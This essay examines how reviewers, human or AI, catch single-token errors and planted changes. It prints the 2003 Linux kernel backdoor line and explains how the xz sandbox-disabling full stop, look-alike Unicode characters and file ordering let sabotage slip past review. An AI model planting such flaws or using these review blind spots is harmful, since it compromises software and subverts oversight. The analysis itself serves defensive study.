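# Overseeing outputs where one changed token flips correctness

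## What it means for one token to decide correctness

A single symbol can decide whether a whole text is correct. In the programming language C, the line `if (value == 100)` runs the code that follows only if `value` equals 100. Removing one equals sign turns it into `if (value = 100)`, which sets `value` to 100. The condition is then always true, because C treats every number except zero as true. MITRE's *CWE-481*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, shows this mistake in a function that is meant to accept only 100 but accepts every number.

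A single symbol can also decide correctness outside programming. A comma can determine who owes money under a contract, and a minus sign can turn a loss into a gain in a calculation. Overseeing such outputs means checking them before anyone relies on them, whether a person or a language model wrote them. This is hard because nearly everything the reviewer reads is correct, and the one wrong symbol usually looks ordinary too.

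### Basic terms

A *token* is a small unit of text, such as a word, a number, an operator or a punctuation mark. The term has an exact meaning in C, where Microsoft's *C Tokens* defines it as source text that the compiler (the program that translates code for the machine) does not break down further. By that definition, `if (value == 100)` has six tokens, including `==`, which is two characters long. Language models process and generate text in their own tokens, which may not match the compiler's.

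A *decisive change* is a change to one token, or very few, that makes a correct output incorrect. Reviewers may have a *trusted version*, an earlier or independent copy that they believe is correct. If they do, they can produce a *diff*, a display of the differences between two versions of a text. A *backdoor* is a change that someone plants to gain hidden access or control. An *AI reviewer* is a language model, alone or with tools, that reads an output and reports suspected faults.

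### Sensitivity

Some kinds of text are far more exposed to decisive changes than others, and theoretical computer science has a measure for this. Let x be a text with n positions and let f be a verdict on it, say 1 for correct and 0 for incorrect. The *sensitivity* of f at x is the number of positions i at which changing x_i, and nothing else, flips f(x):

s(f, x) = the number of positions i for which f(x) ≠ f(x with only position i changed)

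The usual mathematical setting, as in *Parity, Sensitivity, and Transformers* (2026), has only the symbols 0 and 1, so each position allows exactly one change. Real text allows many changes at each position, and a position counts as deciding correctness if at least one of them flips the verdict.

The parity of a 21-bit text is whether it contains an even number of ones. Flipping any one bit changes the answer, so every such text has a sensitivity of 21. *Understanding the Parameter Space Geometry of Transformers Encoding Boolean Functions* (2026) distinguishes the average, maximum and minimum sensitivity over all texts of a given length, and for parity all three are equal.

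An essay grade is closer to a majority vote, where the verdict is 1 if more than half of the bits are ones, because many parts each contribute a little. With 15 ones out of 21, no single flip changes the outcome, and the average sensitivity over all 21-bit strings is only about 3.7. Hahn and Rofin (2024), in *Why are Sensitive Functions Hard for Transformers?*, give the general rule that this average grows with the square root of the length. Borderline cases are the exception. With 11 ones and 10 zeros, flipping any of the 11 ones changes the outcome, and an essay one mark above the pass line is in much the same position.

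Hahn, Jurafsky and Futrell (2021) applied the idea to ordinary sentences in *Sensitivity as a Complexity Measure for Sequence Classification Tasks*. They took short film reviews, used one language model to propose ten replacements for a word, and used another to judge whether each new version was still positive. No proposed replacement for "gorgeous" changed the verdict on "a gorgeous, witty, seductive movie". The verdict depended much more on "funny" in "a painfully funny ode to bad behavior", where substituting "bleak" made the review negative. Their measure gives more weight to replacements that are likely in normal writing. This makes sense for studying language but suits oversight less well, because the harmful change may be one that hardly anyone would write.

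If the verdict is instead 1 only when all 21 bits are ones, every part must be right. At the single correct text the sensitivity is 21, as high as parity's. With one wrong bit it drops to 1, since only repairing that bit changes the verdict, and with two or more it is 0. *Lower Bounds for Chain-of-Thought Reasoning in Hard-Attention Transformers* (Amiri, Huang and colleagues, 2025) notes that once any one bit of this function's input is set to 0, the other bits cannot change the output. Almost every possible text has at least two zeros, so the average sensitivity is about 0.00002.

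Average sensitivity can therefore hide the fragility completely. It matters for what models learn easily, and Hahn and Rofin proved a result linking high average sensitivity to difficulty for transformers, the type of network behind most language models. But a reviewer judges one particular text, which is usually correct or nearly correct, and this kind of verdict is highly sensitive to changes in such texts.

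### Why working programs are fragile

One wrong part can break a working program. Its brackets have to match, its comparisons have to point the right way, and its later steps depend on the results of earlier ones. A random string of tokens, by contrast, is already broken, and almost no single change will turn it into a program that does its job.

Changing one bit of a program can have drastic effects. In *On the cruelty of really teaching computing science* (1988), Edsger Dijkstra attributed this to the difference between digital and analogue systems. A violinist who puts a finger slightly wrong plays slightly out of tune, but Dijkstra argued that no useful measure of distance between programs makes small changes have small effects.

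One changed token can decide whether a program is correct, but many changes to programs have no noticeable effect. In *Software Mutational Robustness*, Schulte, Fry and colleagues (2012) randomly deleted, copied or swapped statements or machine instructions in 22 programs with more than 150,000 lines of code between them, then ran the programs' own 23,151 tests. On average, 36.8% of the edits left the test results unchanged, and even in the least tolerant program, 21.2% did. Some of these edits may have introduced errors that the tests missed. Others were clearly harmless, such as swapping the order in which a sorting routine sorts the left and right halves of a list.

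So a real program is less brittle than an output that is correct only if every part is right. It is hard to tell from these figures how much less brittle, partly because the edits moved whole statements or instructions instead of single tokens. Random edits also measure something different from sensitivity, because a program may still work after nearly every random edit to a line but fail after one particular change to it.

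### The one-line change test

Mark Miller, a computer scientist, proposed a practical estimate that lets a person choose the alteration. The proposal comes from the 2007 security review of Pvote, a small voting-machine program, in which experts also searched for bugs inserted on purpose. The test goes as follows:

1. Pick lines of the program at random.
2. For each one, let someone alter that line however they like, while leaving the rest of the program alone.
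3. Record how often they can break a security requirement, for example that the machine must count every vote as cast.

The share of lines at which they succeed estimates the program's sensitivity, measured by line instead of by token, with a program counted as correct if it meets the requirement. If they succeed on 12 lines out of 40, the estimate is 30%, with a margin of sampling error of about 14 percentage points either way. It is better treated as a lower bound, because a person who fails to break the requirement may only have missed a way to do it. The estimate also depends on the requirement, since a line that doesn't affect the vote count might still reveal how somebody voted.

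A low share helps reviewers because most single-line mistakes then leave the requirement intact. Reviewers still have to search for the dangerous lines, though, because the estimate covers the program as a whole and does not identify those outside the sample.

### Why spot checks fail

Judging a whole text by reading part of it is a sensible way to look for widespread sloppiness but a bad way to look for one decisive token. Suppose a reviewer reads a random 10% of a text and recognises every error in that part. If the text contains a single decisive token, the reviewer has a 10% chance of catching it. If it contains 50 errors scattered at random, the reviewer has a 90% chance of missing each one, but the probability of catching at least one is 1 − 0.9^50, or about 99.5%. On average the reviewer will find five, which is enough reason to send the whole text back.

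Election auditors have worked through the same arithmetic because counting paper ballots by hand is expensive. *On Estimating the Size of a Statistical Audit* (Rivest, 2006) estimates that when b of n items are bad, an auditor must check about n(1 − e^(−3/b)) items to have a 95% chance of finding at least one bad one. That is about 6% of the items when 50 are bad, 26% when 10 are bad, and 95% when only one is bad.

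Auditors can accept this because a little fraud seldom changes who won. Aslam, Popa and Rivest say in *On Estimating the Size and Confidence of a Statistical Audit* that finding out whether any fraud occurred would require testing everything. They aim only to rule out fraud large enough to change the outcome, and they calculate that size from the margin of victory. In their example, a candidate wins by 1% in a county with 400 precincts. If nobody would dare shift more than a fifth of the votes in any precinct, a cheat would have to corrupt about 10 precincts, and a sample of 103 has a 95% chance of including at least one of them. In a text with a decisive token, one bad item is enough to change the result, so b is 1 and sampling saves almost nothing.

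Both calculations also assume that the reader recognises every error in the sample. Aslam and colleagues assume that an audit of a precinct always gives the right answer, which is a fair simplification for a hand count but a generous one for reading code. If the reader of the 10% sample recognises only half of the errors in it, the chance of catching a single wrong token falls to 5%, while the chance of catching at least one of 50 errors is still about 92%. The reader's lapses therefore matter much more when there is only one error to find. Reading all of the text removes the sampling problem, but the chance of catching the error still depends on how reliably the reader recognises it.

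### Accidents, planted changes and two separate tasks

The same wrong symbol can get into a text by accident or on purpose. MITRE says the single equals sign is generally a typo, since the two operators look so alike, and that it usually causes obvious problems when the program runs. The error is likely to remain only in code that is lightly tested and rarely run.

Accidents can still be costly. In 2017 the makers of the cryptocurrency Zcoin disclosed that one extra character in their code had let an attacker spend coins that nobody had minted. IBTimes UK, in *How a single typo let a hacker steal over £500,000 worth of cryptocurrency*, put the attacker's profit at more than $400,000. That typo was an accident, but the single equals sign that someone slipped into a copy of the Linux source code in 2003 looks like an attempted backdoor.

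A planted error may look the same on the page as an accidental one, but the number of errors tends to differ. Careless writers tend to leave several, so finding one is a reason to look for more. Aslam and colleagues assume that an adversary corrupts as few items as necessary, and they design their audit for that case because it is the hardest. They expect an audit built to catch fraud to uncover most systematic accidents as well. But a good record against ordinary mistakes is only weak evidence that an audit will catch planted ones.

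Reviewing also involves the separate tasks of finding the error and judging its effect. The Zcoin team knew something was wrong because the totals of coins minted and coins spent did not match, but they could not tell from the totals which character in the code was responsible. A diff shows exactly what changed, but the reader still has to decide whether the change matters, which can take some knowledge of the program. C programmers sometimes put an assignment inside a condition on purpose, for instance to store the next character of a file and test it in one step. A single equals sign there does not prove a mistake, so a reviewer can look directly at the decisive token and still approve it.

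Two rates describe a reviewer's performance. The *hit rate*, also called recall, is the share of faulty items the reviewer flags. The *false alarm rate* is the share of clean items the reviewer flags. Neither means much alone, since a reviewer who flags everything scores 100% on both.

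## Comparing a text with a trusted version

A reviewer who has a trusted version of a text can use a diff to list every place where the two versions differ. The reviewer can then find a decisive change without reading the whole text, and won't miss it as they might by checking only a sample.

### How a diff works

Most diff programs compare texts line by line. They look for the longest series of lines that appears in both versions in the same order, and they mark every other line as removed (with a minus sign) or added (with a plus sign). If the old version has m lines, the new one has n, and the two share L lines, the diff contains m − L removed lines and n − L added ones. Changing a single character counts as removing one line and adding another:

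```
- if (value == 100)
+ if (value = 100)
```

Many diff viewers also highlight the characters that differ within a line. Lawyers compare contract drafts in much the same way and call the result a redline.

Checksums are a quicker way to compare files. A *checksum* is a short number that a program calculates from the contents of a file, and almost any change to the file will change the number. Checksums can show that two copies differ but not where, which is enough for an automatic check on a large collection of files. Someone can then run a diff on any file that doesn't match.

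Neither method finds an error that was already in the trusted version, since both texts then contain it.

### The Linux kernel in 2003

In 2003 the developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, kept the master copy of its source code in a system called BitKeeper. Some developers refused to use BitKeeper because it was closed-source, so BitMover, the company behind it, also published a copy in an older system called CVS. Every night a program compared checksums of the public CVS copy with those of BitMover's internal one and sent an email if they differed. BitMover's Larry McVoy had already put tools in place that August to check the CVS copy, because users had found out-of-date files, not because of any concern about attackers (McVoy, 2003, *BK2CVS problem (fixed)*).

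On 5 November the nightly check flagged the file `kernel/exit.c`. McVoy ran tests to rule out a fault in BitMover's own conversion program, restored the file and told the kernel mailing list. He posted the file's history there in *BK2CVS problem* (McVoy, 2003). It had three unexpected entries from the day before. The first added two lines, the second removed 58, and the third put 58 back, with a comment apologising for having worked on the wrong file. All three carried the name of David Miller, a kernel developer, who denied making them.

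The entries also lacked the note that the conversion from BitKeeper normally added to identify the larger change each edit belonged to. McVoy concluded that somebody had edited the CVS copy directly. His own posts show that the checksum comparison came first, though some later accounts give more of the credit to the missing note or to people reading the code. The technology blog Freedom to Tinker says that McVoy noticed a change without a record of approval, while Boucher and Anderson's *Trojan Source* says that experienced developers saw the vulnerability.

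At this point nobody on the list knew what the two lines did. McVoy's report, sent at 20:45 UTC, called the incident "not a big deal" and did not include them. A reader asked what they were, out of curiosity, and at 22:23 McVoy posted a diff between the good and bad versions:

```
+ if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
+         retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines belong to a function that programs call to wait for another process to finish. The single equals sign sets `current->uid`, the user ID of the running program, to 0, the ID of the administrator account, which has unrestricted access. The lines otherwise look like a routine check that returns an error for an odd combination of options. C evaluates the part after `&&` only if the part before it is true, so the change affected only programs that passed exactly that combination. Anyone who knew to use it could take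 over the machine. With `==`, the addition would have done nothing, because the next line of the file overwrites `retval`.

Ten minutes after the diff appeared, a reader named Zwane Mwaikambo replied that the code looked odd. At 22:48 another reader, Chad Kitching, asked whether the code was an attempt to backdoor the kernel. McVoy agreed at 23:03, writing "Good eyes, I missed that" and pointing to the `= 0`.

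So McVoy had removed the backdoor before recognising it as one. A large advantage of having a trusted version is that restoring it undoes even changes that nobody understands.

McVoy later argued with a commenter on LWN, a Linux news site, over who deserved the credit. The commenter had attributed the catch to the "hundreds of eyeballs" on open-source code. McVoy, posting as lm (2003) in *One attempt thwarted*, called this nonsense, since hundreds of people could have found the change and only BitMover had. The commenter, dlang (2003), replied that BitMover's engineers were among those eyeballs and that McVoy's first post had not mentioned a backdoor. The mailing list partly supports both sides, since an automatic comparison found the change and readers not involved in the comparison worked out what the change was for.

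How far the backdoor could have spread is less certain. In McVoy's thread, Linus Torvalds, who decided what went into the kernel, said it had no route into an official release. Changes reached him either through BitKeeper, whose users would not have worked from the CVS copy, or by email, where changes to core files were read and had to be explained. iabervon (2003), in *An attempt to backdoor the kernel*, was more worried that a trusted developer working from the CVS copy would unknowingly include the two lines in a larger patch. Torvalds might well have accepted two innocent-looking lines among many similar ones. Another commenter replied that this would not happen to developers who used CVS correctly, because its diff command leaves out other people's changes.

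### The full stop in xz

Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, warned of a related danger in the 2003 thread. A patch could claim to fix a bug but open a security hole, perhaps while buried among other plausible changes. Something very similar happened to xz, a widely used compression program. According to *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024), someone using the name Jia Tan spent more than two years becoming a trusted maintainer, then added a backdoor that let an attacker run commands on some Linux machines without logging in. The backdoor became public on 29 March 2024, and people began reviewing Jia Tan's other changes.

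One of those changes concerned Landlock, a Linux feature that lets a program restrict its own access to files and so limits the damage if an attacker takes the program over. The instructions for building xz include a test that checks whether the computer supports Landlock by trying to compile a few lines of C that use it. If those lines fail to compile for any reason, the build continues without the Landlock sandbox.

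Velvindron (2024) established from the project's records that Jia Tan had rewritten this test on 26 February. The stated reason was sensible, as the old test only looked for a file that some systems have without fully supporting Landlock. But the new code included a full stop on a line of its own. That is not valid C, so the compiler always rejected the test and the build always left out the sandbox. No error appeared unless the person building xz had explicitly required the sandbox.

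Commenters on GitHub, the site that hosted the project, spotted the full stop, and sjw (2024) passed the discovery on to a security mailing list early on 30 March. Lasse Collin, the original maintainer of xz, fixed the test that day. The fault probably did little harm, because it affected only copies of version 5.6.1 built with a tool called CMake. sjw did not know of any Linux distribution that built it that way.

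The diff had shown the full stop for 33 days. The part that sjw posted removes three lines and adds 22, one of which is just a full stop. The project's records name Collin as the person who applied the change. The *Timeline* suggests that Collin probably missed the typo, although somebody could have forged the entry. Collin found no sign of forgery in a later review of the project's history, published by Tukaani, the group that develops xz.

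Suspecting sabotage did not always help readers find it. When Dave Anderson posted about the sabotage online, another reader, David Andersen, replied that he had looked at the diff expecting something evil and still had not seen it.

Readers of the kernel list recognised a backdoor in their diff in 25 minutes. The diff had only two lines, and they knew nobody had authorised them, whereas the full stop was in a longer change that came from a trusted colleague with a good explanation. Two incidents can't show which of these differences mattered most.

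### Characters that do not show on screen

A diff program compares the characters stored in a file, but reviewers see only their shapes on a screen. Some different characters look identical, and others are invisible. In 2021 Boucher and Anderson warned 19 companies and organisations that their compilers, editors or code-hosting sites did not protect programmers from such characters. They were mainly concerned about invisible characters in Unicode, the standard for digital text, that control the direction of writing. Documents that mix English with Arabic or Hebrew need these characters, but in source code they can make the text appear on screen in a different order from the one the compiler reads.

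The recipients had 99 days to respond before publication, and nine of them committed to releasing a patch. GitHub announced a banner for affected files in its *Warning about bidirectional Unicode text*. The rival sites Bitbucket and GitLab began to display the hidden characters, as did the editor Visual Studio Code. GitLab and Visual Studio Code also started to mark letters that can be mistaken for other letters.

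Compiler developers disagreed about which tools should catch the risky characters. The Rust compiler now rejects them, and GCC, a widely used C compiler, warns about their misuse by default. The Java team thought editors should handle the problem. The developers of LLVM, another family of compilers, put a check in a separate tool to avoid slowing compilation. Boucher and Anderson prefer protection in the compiler because it covers everyone who compiles the code, whichever editor they use. Their opponents say that a compiler's job is only to compile, and that checking for suspicious code belongs in dedicated tools.

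Warnings are useful only if people don't learn to ignore them. At the researchers' request, GitHub searched more than a billion changes from 2021 for direction characters that lacked a matching end marker. It found 7,444, fewer than eight in a million, but 98.8% of them were false positives. Many probably came from programming tools that inserted the characters clumsily. Boucher and Anderson expect a check in an editor or compiler to do better, partly because toolmakers will correct their output. The remaining 1.2% used similar techniques, but not all were malicious, and one was a security tool's demonstration of the problem.

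The warnings also did not cover look-alike letters. James Fuller, a contributor to the data-transfer program curl, showed this by replacing one letter in a web address with a visually identical one, as part of a larger clean-up of the project's scripts. None of the human reviewers or automatic checks noticed, according to curl's *detecting malicious unicode* (2025). In a reconstruction of the trick, GitHub's diff marked the line as changed, but a person could not see the difference. A reader who expects a real correction there has little reason to look further.

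The curl developers responded with a stricter rule. Nearly all of their files need only the basic characters of English text, so an automatic check now rejects anything else, apart from a short list of exceptions. They first had to replace other characters in their own test files with plain-text codes. Projects with a lot of text in other languages would need a longer list of exceptions, so the check would protect them less.

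GitHub widened its warnings in the same month, extending them to hidden text in general on 1 May (GitHub, 2025) and adding them two weeks later to the page that displays an individual change (GitHub, 2025). These changes did not help with Fuller's trick, because a look-alike letter is visible. GitHub told the curl project that it was working on a fix for that too.

Hidden characters were still a practical problem in 2026. In *Glassworm Is Back*, Makari (2026) reported that a search in March found at least 151 GitHub repositories containing code from one campaign that used them. Makari's claim that virtually every editor shows nothing for these characters seems too broad, since, according to GitHub's notice, Visual Studio Code highlights them by default. But GitHub's warning still leaves the reader to open the file in a suitable editor and investigate, whereas a check like curl's stops the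 change automatically.

### Approval records, signatures and reproducible builds

Comparison works only if people know which version to trust and how it came about. An approval record helps by linking each change to the decision to accept it. If a change has no such record, somebody may have bypassed the normal process, as happened in the kernel's CVS copy. But a record is only weak evidence that the reviewer understood the change. For example, the change that added the full stop in xz had an author, an explanation and a named person who applied it.

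Digital signatures can help detect false names in such records. A developer signs a change with a secret key, and anyone with the matching public key can verify that the holder of the secret key signed exactly that text. Ts'o had been asking McVoy for years to add signatures to BitKeeper, which would have made it much harder to pass off a change as David Miller's. McVoy agreed and already had a design, but was waiting for an event that would make users ask for it.

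A signature identifies the key used to sign a text but doesn't show whether the text is correct. Tukaani's *xz backdoor* (2024) states that Jia Tan created and signed the release files that contained the backdoor, so their signatures were genuine.

Compiled programs are harder to check because most users never see the source code. A *reproducible build* lets people compare a compiled program with its source. The developers publish the source code with the exact tools and settings for compiling it, and remove anything that would vary between computers, such as the time of compilation or the order in which files are read. Independent people can then compile the code themselves, and should get a program that matches the official one bit for bit. If their checksums match, the official program corresponds to the published source. If one doesn't match, either the setups differ or someone has altered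 a program.

This would have caught neither act of sabotage in xz if everyone had started from the same release files, because each person would have compiled the same sabotaged source and obtained the same result. For the main backdoor, the useful comparison was between the release files and the project's public record of its source code. Jia Tan had put a modified build script in the release files but not in the public record, and the rest of the backdoor was harmless without it. The added lines were obvious when sjw compared the script with the clean original from another project.

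Nobody had reason to make that comparison beforehand, because release files for programs like xz normally contain extra scripts that are missing from the public record, and one more did not look suspicious. After the discovery, the Arch Linux distribution switched to building xz directly from the public record, which removes this gap. That change would not have removed the full stop, which was in the public record too.

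### Where comparison ends

A diff saves the most work when the change is small. A completely new text has no old version, so m and L are both zero and the diff consists of all n lines. A reviewer of a program that a language model has just written from a description therefore has to judge the entire text on its merits. The organisers of the Pvote review remarked that a diff would have exposed their bug at once, but a diff requires an earlier version.

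An independent copy can sometimes take the place of an earlier one. If two clerks type in the same paper form, their texts should be identical, and any difference means that at least one of them made a mistake. This does not work for two programmers writing from the same description, because both programs may be correct and still differ on almost every line.

Very large diffs cause a similar problem. If someone changes the indentation throughout a file, L can fall almost to zero even though the program behaves as before. Moving a block of code makes each line appear once as removed and once as added, so a small change inside the block is hard to see. Diff programs can help by ignoring spaces or marking moved lines in a different colour, but ignoring spaces is risky in a language such as Python, where indentation determines which instructions belong to a condition.

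Repeating the mechanical part of a change is often safer than reading it. Suppose a contributor says that a change of 3,000 lines consists of a formatting tool's output and one correction. The reviewer can run the same tool on the trusted version and compare the result with the contributor's text, and the diff should show only the correction. A reproducible build can also check a change that only reformats, because the compiled program should stay the same apart from details such as stored line numbers. Neither method helps with a large change meant to alter what the program does. The reviewer then has to read the changed lines, and may be little better at finding errors in them than in a new text of the same length.

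## What human reviewers catch and miss

A reviewer who has nothing to compare a text with can find a wrong token only by reading. Researchers measure how well people do this by planting faults in programs and counting how many of them programmers find during review. Few of these experiments used single-token faults, but several used faults almost that small.

### Experts searching 100 lines

The 2007 review of Pvote, the voting-machine program behind the one-line change test, included an experiment of this kind. Ka-Ping Yee, who wrote Pvote, and the computer scientist David Wagner placed an easy bug, a medium one and a hard one in a 100-line region. They showed the region to expert reviewers and told them it contained at least one bug.

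One reviewer found the easy and medium bugs within about 70 minutes. Others took two to four hours to find the easy one. Nobody found the hard bug, although the reviewers together spent about 20 hours searching, or 12 minutes per line.

Most of the conditions favoured the reviewers. Wagner described these conditions years later in a message inviting other programmers to try the task. Financial Cryptography reproduced the message in *The Ka-Ping challenge* (2013). Yee had written Pvote to be as easy to verify as possible. The reviewers had a detailed written argument that the program was secure, and they could ask Yee and Wagner questions as they worked.

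The answers were not always reliable, because the experiment imitated sabotage by an insider. Yee and Wagner warned the reviewers to treat them as adversaries who might lie. To save time, they promised to tell the truth about anything the reviewers could have checked independently, such as how the Python language behaves. Wagner also said that they had picked a bug that would survive the usual test before an election, which left reading the code as the main defence. In that test, officials cast a few ballots, typically at least one for each candidate, and check the totals.

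The reviewers, who spent hours on the same 100 lines, mentioned fatigue and how much their work depends on trusting the author. A reviewer who doesn't trust the author has to work out what a line does rather than accept a comment that explains it and move on.

Three bugs and a handful of reviewers are too few to give a useful hit rate. The instructions also said there was "at least one" bug, so reviewers who had found one could not know whether to keep looking. But the experts missed bugs even after spending 12 minutes on each line, which is probably longer than they would spend in any ordinary code review.

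### Two audits of the same program

Students at Rice University did better at a similar task. *Hack-a-Vote* (Bannet, Price and colleagues, 2004) describes a graduate security course in which pairs of students sabotaged a voting program of about 2,000 lines. Each pair then had one week to audit two versions that other pairs had sabotaged. The students already knew the original program, but the university's honour code stopped them from using a diff.

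Two pairs of reviewers audited each version. About two thirds of the hacks were found by both pairs, and all but one of the rest were found by just one pair. A single pair therefore found a little over 80% of the hacks on average, which is the two thirds that both pairs found plus about half of the remaining third.

A fault that is hard for one reader to find is usually hard for the next, so a second audit usually catches less than it would if the auditors' mistakes were independent. With independent mistakes, two pairs of auditors that each miss 17% of the hacks would both miss only about 3% of them. Every expert who looked for Pvote's hard bug missed it, so adding another reader of the same kind might not have helped much.

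The students' task was easier than finding one wrong token. Many of the hacks added or rewrote whole pieces of code, and the instructors' own earlier example had taken about 150 lines. The students could also make what Bannet and colleagues call "mental diffs", comparing the code with their memory of the original. Real auditors rarely have that advantage, and they usually face much more code. One Diebold voting machine ran on more than 50,000 lines. An employee of a firm that had reviewed such machines estimated a 99.9% chance that hidden malicious code would escape notice, but this was an opinion, not a measurement.

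Some pairs found a hack without understanding what it did, including one that could make a candidate disappear from the final count. In a class where everyone knows the code contains sabotage, pointing at a strange line is nearly as good as explaining it. But in an ordinary review the author may offer an innocent explanation, and a reviewer who can't say what harm the line does may well accept it.

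### Familiar faults and missing checks

Programmers are much better at spotting a fault if they have seen the same pattern before. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021) asked 146 people to review a change of about 140 lines to a program that manages employees' holidays. Of these, 105 had at least three years of professional experience. The researchers did not mention security at first, and gave each person one of two versions at random.

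One version contained an *SQL injection*, a famous textbook weakness. The program pasted users' text into a database command, so a user could type something that changed the command. The other version let employees buy extra days of holiday but never checked that the number was positive. An employee who "bought" −5 days would receive money instead of paying it.

After the first review, the researchers warned everyone that the code contained a security weakness, without saying which kind. Anyone who thought they had missed it could look again.

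| | SQL injection | Missing check for a negative number |
|---|---|---|
| Reviewers | 80 | 66 |
| Found it in the first review | 52 (65%) | 14 (21%) |
| Found it only after the warning | 13 (16%) | 7 (11%) |
| Never found it | 15 (19%) | 45 (68%) |

Both weaknesses arise because the program trusts user input, and both were fully visible in the code. Even after the warning, 60 people had not found the weakness in the code they reviewed. For 45 of them, that weakness was the missing check.

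The warning helped mainly with the familiar weakness. After the warning, 13 of the 28 people who had overlooked the SQL injection found it, compared with 7 of the 52 who had overlooked the missing check. Many of those 13 said they had needed a reminder to think about security. A reminder was not enough for the others, who did not know what to look for or settled on the wrong thing. Eight people with the missing check said they had mistaken an unrelated bug for the security weakness. The researchers had added that bug to test whether participants were paying attention.

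Some of the improvement may have come from reading the code twice, since no group reviewed it again without a warning. None of the 70 people who missed the unrelated bug in the first review reported it in the second, which suggests that rereading alone did little. But this is weak evidence, because by then they were looking for a security problem.

People who often reviewed code, or who said they thought about security when writing it, were more likely to find the weakness during the first review. Years of professional experience made no clear difference.

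A missing check is similar to a one-token change because in both cases the code looks normal, and the reviewer has to think of the particular input that makes it fail. But adding the check takes several tokens, and there is no wrong symbol to notice, as there would be with a changed operator.

Telling reviewers to look for security problems doesn't guarantee a good result either. Braz and colleagues cite a 2013 experiment by Edmundson and others, which found that security-focused reviews of web applications containing SQL injections were relatively ineffective. So 65% may be generous even for this well-known weakness.

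### A one-token fault and its place in the review

Fregnan, Braz and colleagues (2022), in *First Come First Served*, tested a fault that really was a single token. They asked 106 people, most of them software developers, to review a change spread over five short files. One file calculated discounts for members of a shop. According to a comment just above the code, members at levels 2 to 4 should get 10% off, but the condition read:

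```
if (membershipLevel > 2 && membershipLevel < 5)
```

The first operator should have been `>=`. As written, the code gave members at level 2 no discount. Only 52 of the 106 reviewers (49%) reported the fault, although any of them could have found it by comparing the condition with the comment. Nobody had told them the code contained defects.

Reviewers found the fault much more often when the file containing it came first. In that position, 34 of 56 reviewers found it (61%), compared with 18 of 50 (36%) when the file came last. Fregnan and colleagues report this as 64% lower odds, where the odds are the number of reviewers who found the fault divided by the number who missed it (34/22 when the file came first and 18/32 when it came last). The share of reviewers who found it fell by about two fifths.

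The change contained a second fault, a missing `break` statement that made the program overcharge for deliveries to the UK. When the discount fault was in the first file, this one was in the last, and vice versa. When the missing `break` was in the first file, 26 of 50 reviewers found it, compared with 24 of 56 when it was in the last. This difference could easily be due to chance, so the experiment shows a clear effect of position only for the discount fault.

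Waning attention is a plausible reason why the position of the discount fault affected whether reviewers found it. The first file was visible on their screens for an average of 8.6 minutes and the last for 6.1, though all five were similar in length. Nearly three quarters of the reviewers thought the fault's position had not influenced whether they found it.

The same pattern appears in comments on real projects. Developers usually submit their work as a *pull request*, a set of changes that others review before the project accepts it, and the common review tools list the changed files alphabetically. Fregnan and colleagues looked at 219,476 pull requests from 138 projects and found that later files received fewer comments. This held after they controlled for the size of each file's changes and for test files, which attract few comments and tend to come last.

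The evidence that file order lets many more bugs through is weaker. Rahman, Codabux and Roy (2026), in *Does Order Matter?*, checked whether the next change to each file in 330,343 pull requests was a bug fix. It was for 56.7% of files in first position and 61.5% of those in thirtieth, and the overall link with position was very weak. They identified bug fixes by words such as "fix" and "error" in the developers' descriptions, a crude measure that counted more than half of all files as having had a hidden bug. Files were also not ordered at random, so those late in the alphabet may differ in other ways.

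The number of files may matter more than their order. Rahman and colleagues estimate that each additional file in a pull request lowers the odds of any given file receiving a comment by about 8.7%. At that rate, ten more files would lower the odds by about 60%. Reviewers may read a file carefully without commenting on it, but a decisive token probably gets less attention in a large change than in a small one.

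### Why rare faults are easier to miss

Everyone in these experiments received faulty code, so the experiments can't measure the false alarm rate on clean code. They are also very different from ordinary work, where most changes contain no decisive fault and sabotage is extremely rare.

The *base rate* is the share of items that are faulty before anyone looks. Psychologists who study how people search images call it *prevalence*, and they have found that people miss a larger share of targets when targets are rare, which is known as the *prevalence effect*. *Reducing the low-prevalence effect with probe trials* (2026) credits Jeremy Wolfe and colleagues as the first visual search researchers to investigate the effect, in 2005, after radiologists had raised the concern.

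*Comparing Breast Screening Protocols* describes an artificial baggage-screening task in which the miss rate quadrupled when the share of bags containing a target fell from 50% to 1%. If the same increase applied to code review, a reviewer who misses 10% of faults when half of the changes are faulty would miss 40% when 1% are. Targets can be even rarer in real screening. About three or four of every 1,000 women screened for breast cancer in North America have it, according to *Use-inspired basic research in medical image perception*.

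People miss more targets when targets are rare. Training does not remove this effect, which also occurs in radiologists and airport screeners. Researchers disagree about the cause. One explanation is that people who almost never see a target get used to answering "nothing there" and give that answer sooner, or want stronger evidence before they report anything. Another is that their minds wander. In *Low prevalence targets are primarily missed due to mind wandering*, Dewis, Hout and colleagues (2026) had 60 people search for targets that appeared in either 10% or 50% of trials, and attributed most of the misses to mind wandering.

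The right remedy depends on why reviewers miss faults. If they have become too reluctant to report faults, encouraging them to report more will catch more faults but also produce more false alarms. If their minds are wandering, shorter sessions might help them catch more faults without adding false alarms.

Several obvious remedies for missing rare targets in visual search have failed. *Individual differences predict low prevalence visual search performance* summarises seven that Wolfe and colleagues tried, including making people respond more slowly and having two people search together. The only one that improved detection was adding short bursts of searches in which targets were common and people learned whether their answers were right. This also increased false alarms, as expected if it made people more willing to report a target.

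The experimenters also tried adding common targets to the search, but people did not get better at finding the rare ones. This failure is especially relevant to code, because it suggests that the ordinary bugs reviewers often find may not keep them alert to the rare serious ones.

All of this evidence comes from images and, in some studies of drivers, road scenes. Reading code is a different task. An airport screener knows roughly what a knife looks like and spends a short time on each bag, whereas a code reviewer may spend an hour working out what a change does and doesn't know in advance what the fault will look like. The prevalence effect could be smaller or larger in code review.

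The warning in the holiday experiment is an indirect test on code, because it made reviewers almost certain they would find a weakness. After the warning, a quarter of the reviewers who had missed their weakness found it. But the warning also told them what sort of problem to look for, and none of them had first reviewed a long series of clean changes. A proper test would vary how often faults appear over many reviews by the same people.

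### Would maintainers do better?

The volunteers in the two online experiments read strangers' code in return for a small donation to charity. Unlike them, a maintainer reviewing changes to a familiar project knows what the surrounding code is for, can run the program and its tests, and will have to deal with the consequences of a mistake. Braz and colleagues accept that developers might be more attentive when reviewing their own projects, because more is at stake. The success of the Rice students, who knew the original program, also suggests that familiarity helps.

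But the experiments made the task easier in other ways. The changes were short and self-contained, and the researchers left out anyone who abandoned the task or clearly hadn't tried. Pvote's reviewers also knew which 100 lines to read. Braz and colleagues warn that their results might not hold for large changes, or for changes that deal with several things at once, which are harder to review.

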